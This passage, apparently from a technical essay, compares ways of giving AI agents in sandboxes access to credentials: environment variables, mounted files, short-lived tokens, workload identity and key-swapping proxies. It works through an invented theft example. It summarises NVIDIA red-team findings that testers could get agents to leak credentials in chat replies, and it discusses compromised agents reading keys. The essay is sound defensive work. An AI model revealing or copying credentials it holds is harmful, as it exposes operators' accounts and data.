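| Who can read the real credential? | Nearly every process in the container | Any process whose account may open the file | Any process that can read the token's file or variable | The proxy and the approved host |
| Where does a stolen copy work? | Anywhere | Anywhere | Anywhere | Only through the proxy |
| For how long? | Until the key expires or its owner revokes it | Until the key expires or its owner revokes it | Until the token expires, often within an hour | Until the proxy deletes the surrogate's record |
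| What may the holder do? | Whatever the key permits | Whatever the key permits | Whatever the token permits | Whatever the key permits and the proxy lets through |
| How does the operator rotate it? | Replace the key and restart the container | Replace the file, which programs then have to read again | The issuer supplies new tokens automatically | Replace the key at the proxy |
| What must somebody build and maintain? | Almost nothing | A mount and file permissions | Token exchange and renewal for each service | A proxy, a certificate authority, network routing and a rule for each service |

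A short-lived token can still have broad permissions. Someone who steals a one-hour token with full permissions can do anything the operator can until it expires, whereas someone who steals a 90-day token that can only file tickets is limited to filing tickets for those 90 days.

### Mounted files and rotation

A mounted file does little to protect a key from a compromised agent, because the agent's shell can usually open it.

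Mounting the file in a different container helps more. In an example from the Kubernetes documentation on Secrets, one container handles users' requests and another holds a signing key and signs what the first sends it. The first container cannot read the key, so an attacker who takes it over has to trick it into requesting a signature, which may be harder than getting it to read a file. The swapping proxy separates an API key from the agent in the same way.

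Operators who use Kubernetes must also protect the file's source. By default, Kubernetes stores Secrets, its objects for keys and passwords, unencrypted in its database. Anyone allowed to start containers in a namespace, a section of the cluster, can use that permission to read every Secret there.

Files have a clearer advantage when the operator replaces a key. According to Microsoft's *Secrets rotation of environment variables and mounted secrets in pods*, an environment variable keeps the old value until the operator restarts the container, whereas Kubernetes updates a mounted file automatically. The update can take a while, and files mounted with the `subPath` option don't receive it. A program that read the key at startup must also reread the file to get the new one.

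With a proxy, the operator can in principle change the key in one place while every container keeps its surrogate. Docker's *Authenticate command-line tools* states that existing sandboxes do not receive a new value for a global secret, but other Docker documentation says they do on local machines, so Docker users should test a rotation before relying on it.

Deleting a surrogate leaves the real key valid at the service, so Docker tells users to rotate or revoke a credential at its provider when they no longer need it.

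### A theft at minute 10

The numbers in this example are invented. A sandbox runs for 30 minutes. The real key is valid for 90 days from the moment the sandbox starts, and the short-lived token for 60 minutes. An attacker takes control of the container at minute 10 and copies whatever credential it holds. Nobody notices, and the proxy deletes the surrogate's record when the sandbox ends. The stolen value then keeps working for:

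```
Real key:   90 days − 10 min = 129,600 − 10 = 129,590 minutes
Token:      60 − 10                         = 50 minutes
Surrogate:  30 − 10                         = 20 minutes
```

The attacker's own machine cannot reach the proxy, so the surrogate works only from inside the container:

| Arrangement | Time left after the theft | Of which usable from another machine | Time left after the sandbox ends |
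|---|---|---|---|
| Environment variable | 129,590 minutes | 129,590 minutes | 129,570 minutes |
| Mounted file | 129,590 minutes | 129,590 minutes | 129,570 minutes |
| 60-minute token | 50 minutes | 50 minutes | 30 minutes |
| Surrogate | 20 minutes | 0 minutes | 0 minutes |

Most of the improvement comes from the token's short lifetime. Replacing the 90-day key with the 60-minute token cuts the exposure by a factor of about 2,600. The surrogate removes the last 30 minutes of exposure and prevents the attacker from using the credential on a machine the operator cannot monitor. If the operator could revoke the token when the sandbox ends, it would also stop working after 20 minutes, but the attacker could still use it from anywhere until then.

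Now suppose that all four credentials permit the same actions, and that the attacker files five fake tickets a minute for as long as possible:

| Arrangement | Fake tickets while the sandbox runs | Fake tickets afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| Environment variable | 20 × 5 = 100 | 129,570 × 5 = 647,850 |
| Mounted file | 20 × 5 = 100 | 129,570 × 5 = 647,850 |
| 60-minute token | 20 × 5 = 100 | 30 × 5 = 150 |
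| Surrogate | 20 × 5 = 100 | 0 |

The middle column is the same for all four arrangements because the service accepts the attacker's requests during the session, however the key reaches it. A single request can delete a project, and none of them prevents that. Preventing it requires narrower permissions or a rule at the proxy, as explained in the earlier discussion of approved hosts.

The 90-day figure applies only if nobody notices the theft. If the operator discovers it after a week and revokes the key at once, the exposure falls to seven days, which is still about 200 times as long as the token's 50 minutes.

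### Workload identity

Operators often get short-lived tokens through workload identity. The program proves which workload it is, and the service gives it a brief token in return, so nobody has to store a long-lived key for that service. Anthropic's *Workload Identity Federation* describes the exchange for programs that call Claude. For an agent in a Kubernetes container, it goes like this:

1. Kubernetes puts a signed identity token in a file in the container. The token names its issuer and the workload.
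2. Anthropic's SDK sends the identity token to Anthropic.
3. Anthropic checks the signature with the issuer's public keys, then compares the token's contents with a rule that the operator has set up.
4. Anthropic returns an access token, which the SDK sends with each request and renews before it expires.

The rule sets the access token's lifetime, from 60 seconds to 24 hours, with a default of one hour. It also sets the token's permissions. The default token is short-lived but has the same permissions as an ordinary API key. OpenAI's *Workload identity federation* describes a similar exchange, in which the operator can give a token fewer permissions than the account behind it has.

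Anthropic cautions that the method is only as strong as the provider that signs the identity tokens. For an agent, it also matters where the exchange takes place. In the steps above, both the identity token and the access token are in the container, where a compromised agent can read them. Ghosh nonetheless groups workload identity with proxies that add headers, as versions of the old idea of keeping a secret out of the process that uses it.

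Anthropic limits what an attacker can do with a copied identity token. By default, it accepts a token with a unique ID only once. The access token also lasts no more than twice the time the identity token has left, unless that is under a minute. If the identity token in the example expires at minute 30 and the attacker exchanges it at minute 10, it has 20 minutes left, so the access token lasts at most 40 minutes, until minute 50. However, an attacker who stays in the container can wait for Kubernetes to issue a new identity token and exchange that one too. Under the default rule, an access token obtained just before the sandbox ends could work for up to an hour afterwards.

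Moving to workload identity also requires removing the old key. Anthropic's SDK gives `ANTHROPIC_API_KEY` priority over the identity settings, so if the variable is still set, the program keeps using the long-lived key without any error. OpenAI's Codex gives priority to the identity settings instead.

### Which services accept workload identity

Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) lists limited support as one of the biggest weaknesses of workload identity. Many services do not accept tokens in the OpenID Connect (OIDC) format, which most identity providers issue. A platform that uses such a service has to build its own token exchange, which makes the method hard to adopt. Cloudflare has a commercial interest in this argument because it offers its own programmable proxy as the better solution, but the argument is correct for any service that issues only fixed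 keys. If the ticket service issues only fixed keys, no identity provider can help the operator.

Cloudflare's argument has become weaker for AI models since it was published in April 2026. In June, Anthropic's *Secure access to the Claude Platform with Workload Identity Federation* (2026) announced general availability of workload identity federation for all of the company's API endpoints. GitHub now lists this method as an alternative to a stored key for running Claude in its agent workflows. OpenAI supports it for its API, although the version for Codex is still in beta.

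An API provider may also accept only some types of short-lived credentials. According to OpenAI's *Configuring workload identity federation for AWS*, OpenAI accepts OIDC tokens issued by AWS but not SigV4-signed requests or temporary AWS keys. An operator whose AWS setup produces only temporary keys therefore has to set up OIDC tokens first.

Developers can build a similar exchange for GitHub with a GitHub App, an identity that an organisation registers for a program. *GitHub App Authentication for the GitHub Agent* (Aradhyula, 2026) describes how one agent does this. The agent's token provider signs a statement with the App's private key and exchanges the signed statement for a token that lasts 60 minutes. It keeps the token in memory and replaces it five minutes before it expires. The agent's developers added this as an alternative to personal access tokens, which they had to rotate every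 month.

fnox's *GitHub App*, the documentation of a command-line tool for secrets, adds that GitHub itself sets the one-hour limit and that the tool can revoke a token early if it has kept a copy. The operator can also limit each token to chosen permissions and repositories, according to fnox.

The short-lived tokens come from the App's private key, which can produce new ones until its owner revokes it. If that key is in the agent's container, an attacker can copy it and create tokens for months. The exchange of key for token should therefore happen outside the container, and only the token should go in.

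### What the proxy costs

Anthropic lists keeping credentials in one secure location, instead of in every agent's container, as a benefit of the proxy. This makes them easier to rotate and audit, but it also means that a single break-in can expose all of them. Suppose that ten agents have four keys each and that no two agents share a key. An attacker who compromises one container with real keys in it gets four, while an attacker who compromises a proxy that serves all ten agents gets 40.

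Attempts to exploit LiteLLM, the gateway whose releases attackers had poisoned, also show that such a store is an attractive target. *CVE-2026-42208* (Clark, 2026) describes a flaw that let anyone who could reach a LiteLLM server query its database without logging in. Clark's team at Sysdig, a security company, recorded the first attempt to exploit it 36 hours after GitHub's global database listed the flaw, and more than five days after LiteLLM published its own advisory. The requests went straight to the three tables that hold access keys, model providers' credentials and the server's settings. The team saw nobody use a stolen key afterwards, so the incident is evidence that attackers look for these credentials, but doesn't establish that they obtained any.

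Clark recommends keeping such gateways on an internal network. That is good advice for a proxy too, but it does not help against a compromised container, because the container must be able to reach the proxy. Before the proxy decides whether to trust a request, it parses input from code that an attacker may control. A similar flaw in a swapping proxy could expose its keys to the agents it is supposed to keep them from.

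Giving each agent its own proxy, as in Maiti's sidecar design, limits the damage from a break-in. In the invented example, an attacker who broke into one sidecar would get four keys instead of 40, but the operator would have ten proxies to update.

A proxy on a laptop can also have access to more than the agent needs. According to Infisical's *Local proxy*, the proxy acts as the logged-in user and can read the same secrets as that user.

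Interception adds a second kind of exposure, because the proxy can read everything the agent sends and receives. For a coding agent, this includes source code and the conversation with the model. According to SC Media's *LiteLLM exploited within 36 hours of disclosure via SQL injection bug*, a gateway like LiteLLM holds prompts and responses as well as keys.

The proxy may also write this material to disk. devsandbox logs each request with its headers and body in compressed files of up to 50 MB, and keeps at most five. The bodies are encoded in base64, which anyone can decode. These logs are useful after an incident, but they need the same protection as the code and data that pass through the proxy.

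Anthropic describes two ways to avoid interception. If the operator sets `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, Claude Code sends its model requests to the proxy as plain HTTP, and the proxy adds the key. This works only for calls to the model. For other services, the operator can provide a tool that runs outside the container and makes the authenticated requests itself. For example, the agent can use the tool to file a ticket without contacting the ticket service directly. But each service needs its own tool, and ordinary software such as Git or an SDK won't use it unless somebody adapts that software.

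Transparent routing works for programs that ignore `HTTP_PROXY`, but programs that pin certificates still reject the proxy's certificate. If an agent depends on such a program, the operator has to give the container a real credential for the service the program calls, and a short-lived token is the best choice.

Each service also needs its own configuration, and mistakes don't always produce a clear error. Corvic's connector for FRED failed because it put the key in a header instead of the URL. With devsandbox, if the variable or file that should supply the key is empty, the proxy silently stops adding the credential. By default, it also leaves an existing header alone, so a surrogate sent by a program reaches the service unless the operator has set `overwrite = true`. Neither devsandbox mistake leaks a key, but someone has to work out why the agent's requests are failing.

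Unlike an environment variable, the proxy is a shared point of failure. If it crashes or its certificate expires, all the agents behind it lose access to every service at once.

### Combining a proxy with short-lived tokens

An operator can put a short-lived token in the proxy instead of a long-lived key. The container then has only a surrogate, and an attacker who breaks into the proxy gets a token that soon expires. Cloudflare criticizes workload identity but notes that it can work together with a proxy.

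Loganathan (2026), in *How Auth Proxy secures network access for LangSmith agent sandboxes*, describes one version. LangSmith's developers found that fixed keys were not enough for agents that act on behalf of different users, so the proxy can fetch credentials when it needs them:

1. Code in the sandbox sends a request to an approved host.
2. If the proxy has no stored credential for that host, it calls an address that the operator has set up and tells it which host and port the request is for.
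3. The operator's service returns the headers to add, for example a token for one user.
4. The proxy adds them, forwards the request and keeps the headers for a set time.

If the operator's service fails or returns a malformed response, the proxy rejects the request instead of sending it without a credential. This is safer than the behavior of devsandbox, which silently omits the credential, and it makes the fault easier to find. The operator has to choose carefully how long the proxy stores each token. If the storage time is longer than the token's lifetime, the proxy will send expired tokens. If the proxy keeps a token for 45 minutes and the user loses access, an agent may continue working under the old permissions for most of that time.

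With the 60-minute token from the example, the combination changes the result of each theft as follows:

| What the attacker steals at minute 10 | Proxy with a 90-day key | Proxy with a 60-minute token |
|---|---|---|
| The surrogate, from the container | 20 minutes, through the proxy | 20 minutes, through the proxy |
| The real credential, from the proxy | 129,590 minutes, from anywhere | 50 minutes, from anywhere |

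This improves only the second row, and only if the refresh token or private key that produces new tokens is kept outside the proxy. In LangSmith's design, the operator's service can hold it. That service then becomes the most valuable target, but the sandbox never needs to contact it.

The real credential can have limited permissions as well as a short lifetime. In an example from devsandbox, GitHub's command-line tool starts with `placeholder` as its token, and the proxy replaces this with a read-only token. A compromised agent could not push code through the proxy, even if the proxy had no rules of its own. Kenney and colleagues similarly recommend separate identities for reading and writing, because moving a token into a vault does not reduce what the token permits.

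Surrogates can also expire. Kilo, which makes a coding agent, gives each sandbox a short-lived encrypted token tied to that sandbox alone. Before forwarding a request, Kilo's proxy checks that Kilo issued the token, that the token allows the destination, and that the request comes from the right sandbox. The third check addresses Hacker News commenters' concern about copied surrogates. This account relies on Kilo's description of its own product.

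### NVIDIA's guidance

NVIDIA's AI Red Team, which attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses, published advice on agents in January and July 2026. The earlier post, NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, separates mandatory controls from recommended ones. Three are mandatory:

- blocking network access to arbitrary sites
- blocking writes to files outside the agent's workspace
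- blocking writes to configuration files anywhere

Secret injection is one of six controls NVIDIA recommends. It means giving the sandbox only the credentials its current task needs, ideally by a route the agent cannot access directly. NVIDIA's example is a broker that issues short-lived tokens on demand, so the recommendation does not favour surrogates over tokens.

Ranking network controls first makes sense because an allowlist protects everything in the container, while a surrogate protects only the keys. But NVIDIA also warns that exposed secrets remain a risk even with network controls, and its later tests support this. *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* reports on six months of NVIDIA's assessments. When network controls stopped testers from sending credentials out directly, they could often still get the agent to reveal them in its chat replies. NVIDIA does not publish how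 many agents it tested or how often this worked.

The July post no longer divides controls into mandatory and recommended, and it is stricter about secrets. It tells operators never to give an agent access to persistent secrets, to use short-lived, narrow tokens when a task needs a credential, and to revoke them as soon as the task is complete. It lists NVIDIA's own product, OpenShell, among the suitable sandboxes, but the advice on secrets does not depend on using OpenShell.

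### When an environment variable is enough

NVIDIA considers environment variables reasonable when only the operator's own code runs in the container, and insecure when the workload can execute arbitrary code. A coding agent can always do the latter, but the harm from losing a particular key may be too small to justify a proxy. Anthropic similarly writes that a developer using Claude Code on a laptop has different requirements from a company that processes many customers' data.

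A developer might try out an agent with a test key for a translation service. The account is separate from any other, contains no data, and stops working once it has spent 20 dollars (again an invented figure). If somebody steals the key at minute 10, the exposure is still 90 days by the calculation above, but the thief can spend at most 20 dollars. Setting up interception for this one key would take an afternoon of work, which is worth more than 20 dollars.

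This reasoning holds only if the account's limit stops further spending, since some services only send a warning when a customer reaches it. The key must also be unable to create other keys, raise its own limit or read anything stored in the account. A thief can still use up the whole allowance, which interrupts the developer's work, or break the service's rules and get the account suspended. These are nuisances for a separate test account, but they could take down the company's website if it runs on the same account.

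The same applies to a key that gives access only to public data and that the provider requires mainly to count requests. It does not apply to a GitHub token, even one for a test repository, if the token can also reach the developer's other repositories.

When the key matters more but a proxy is too much work, a short-lived token is the obvious compromise if the service offers one. In the example, it cut the 129,590 minutes to 50 without interception or a certificate authority. The benefits of a proxy outweigh its drawbacks when the key gives access to customer data and the service issues only long-lived credentials.
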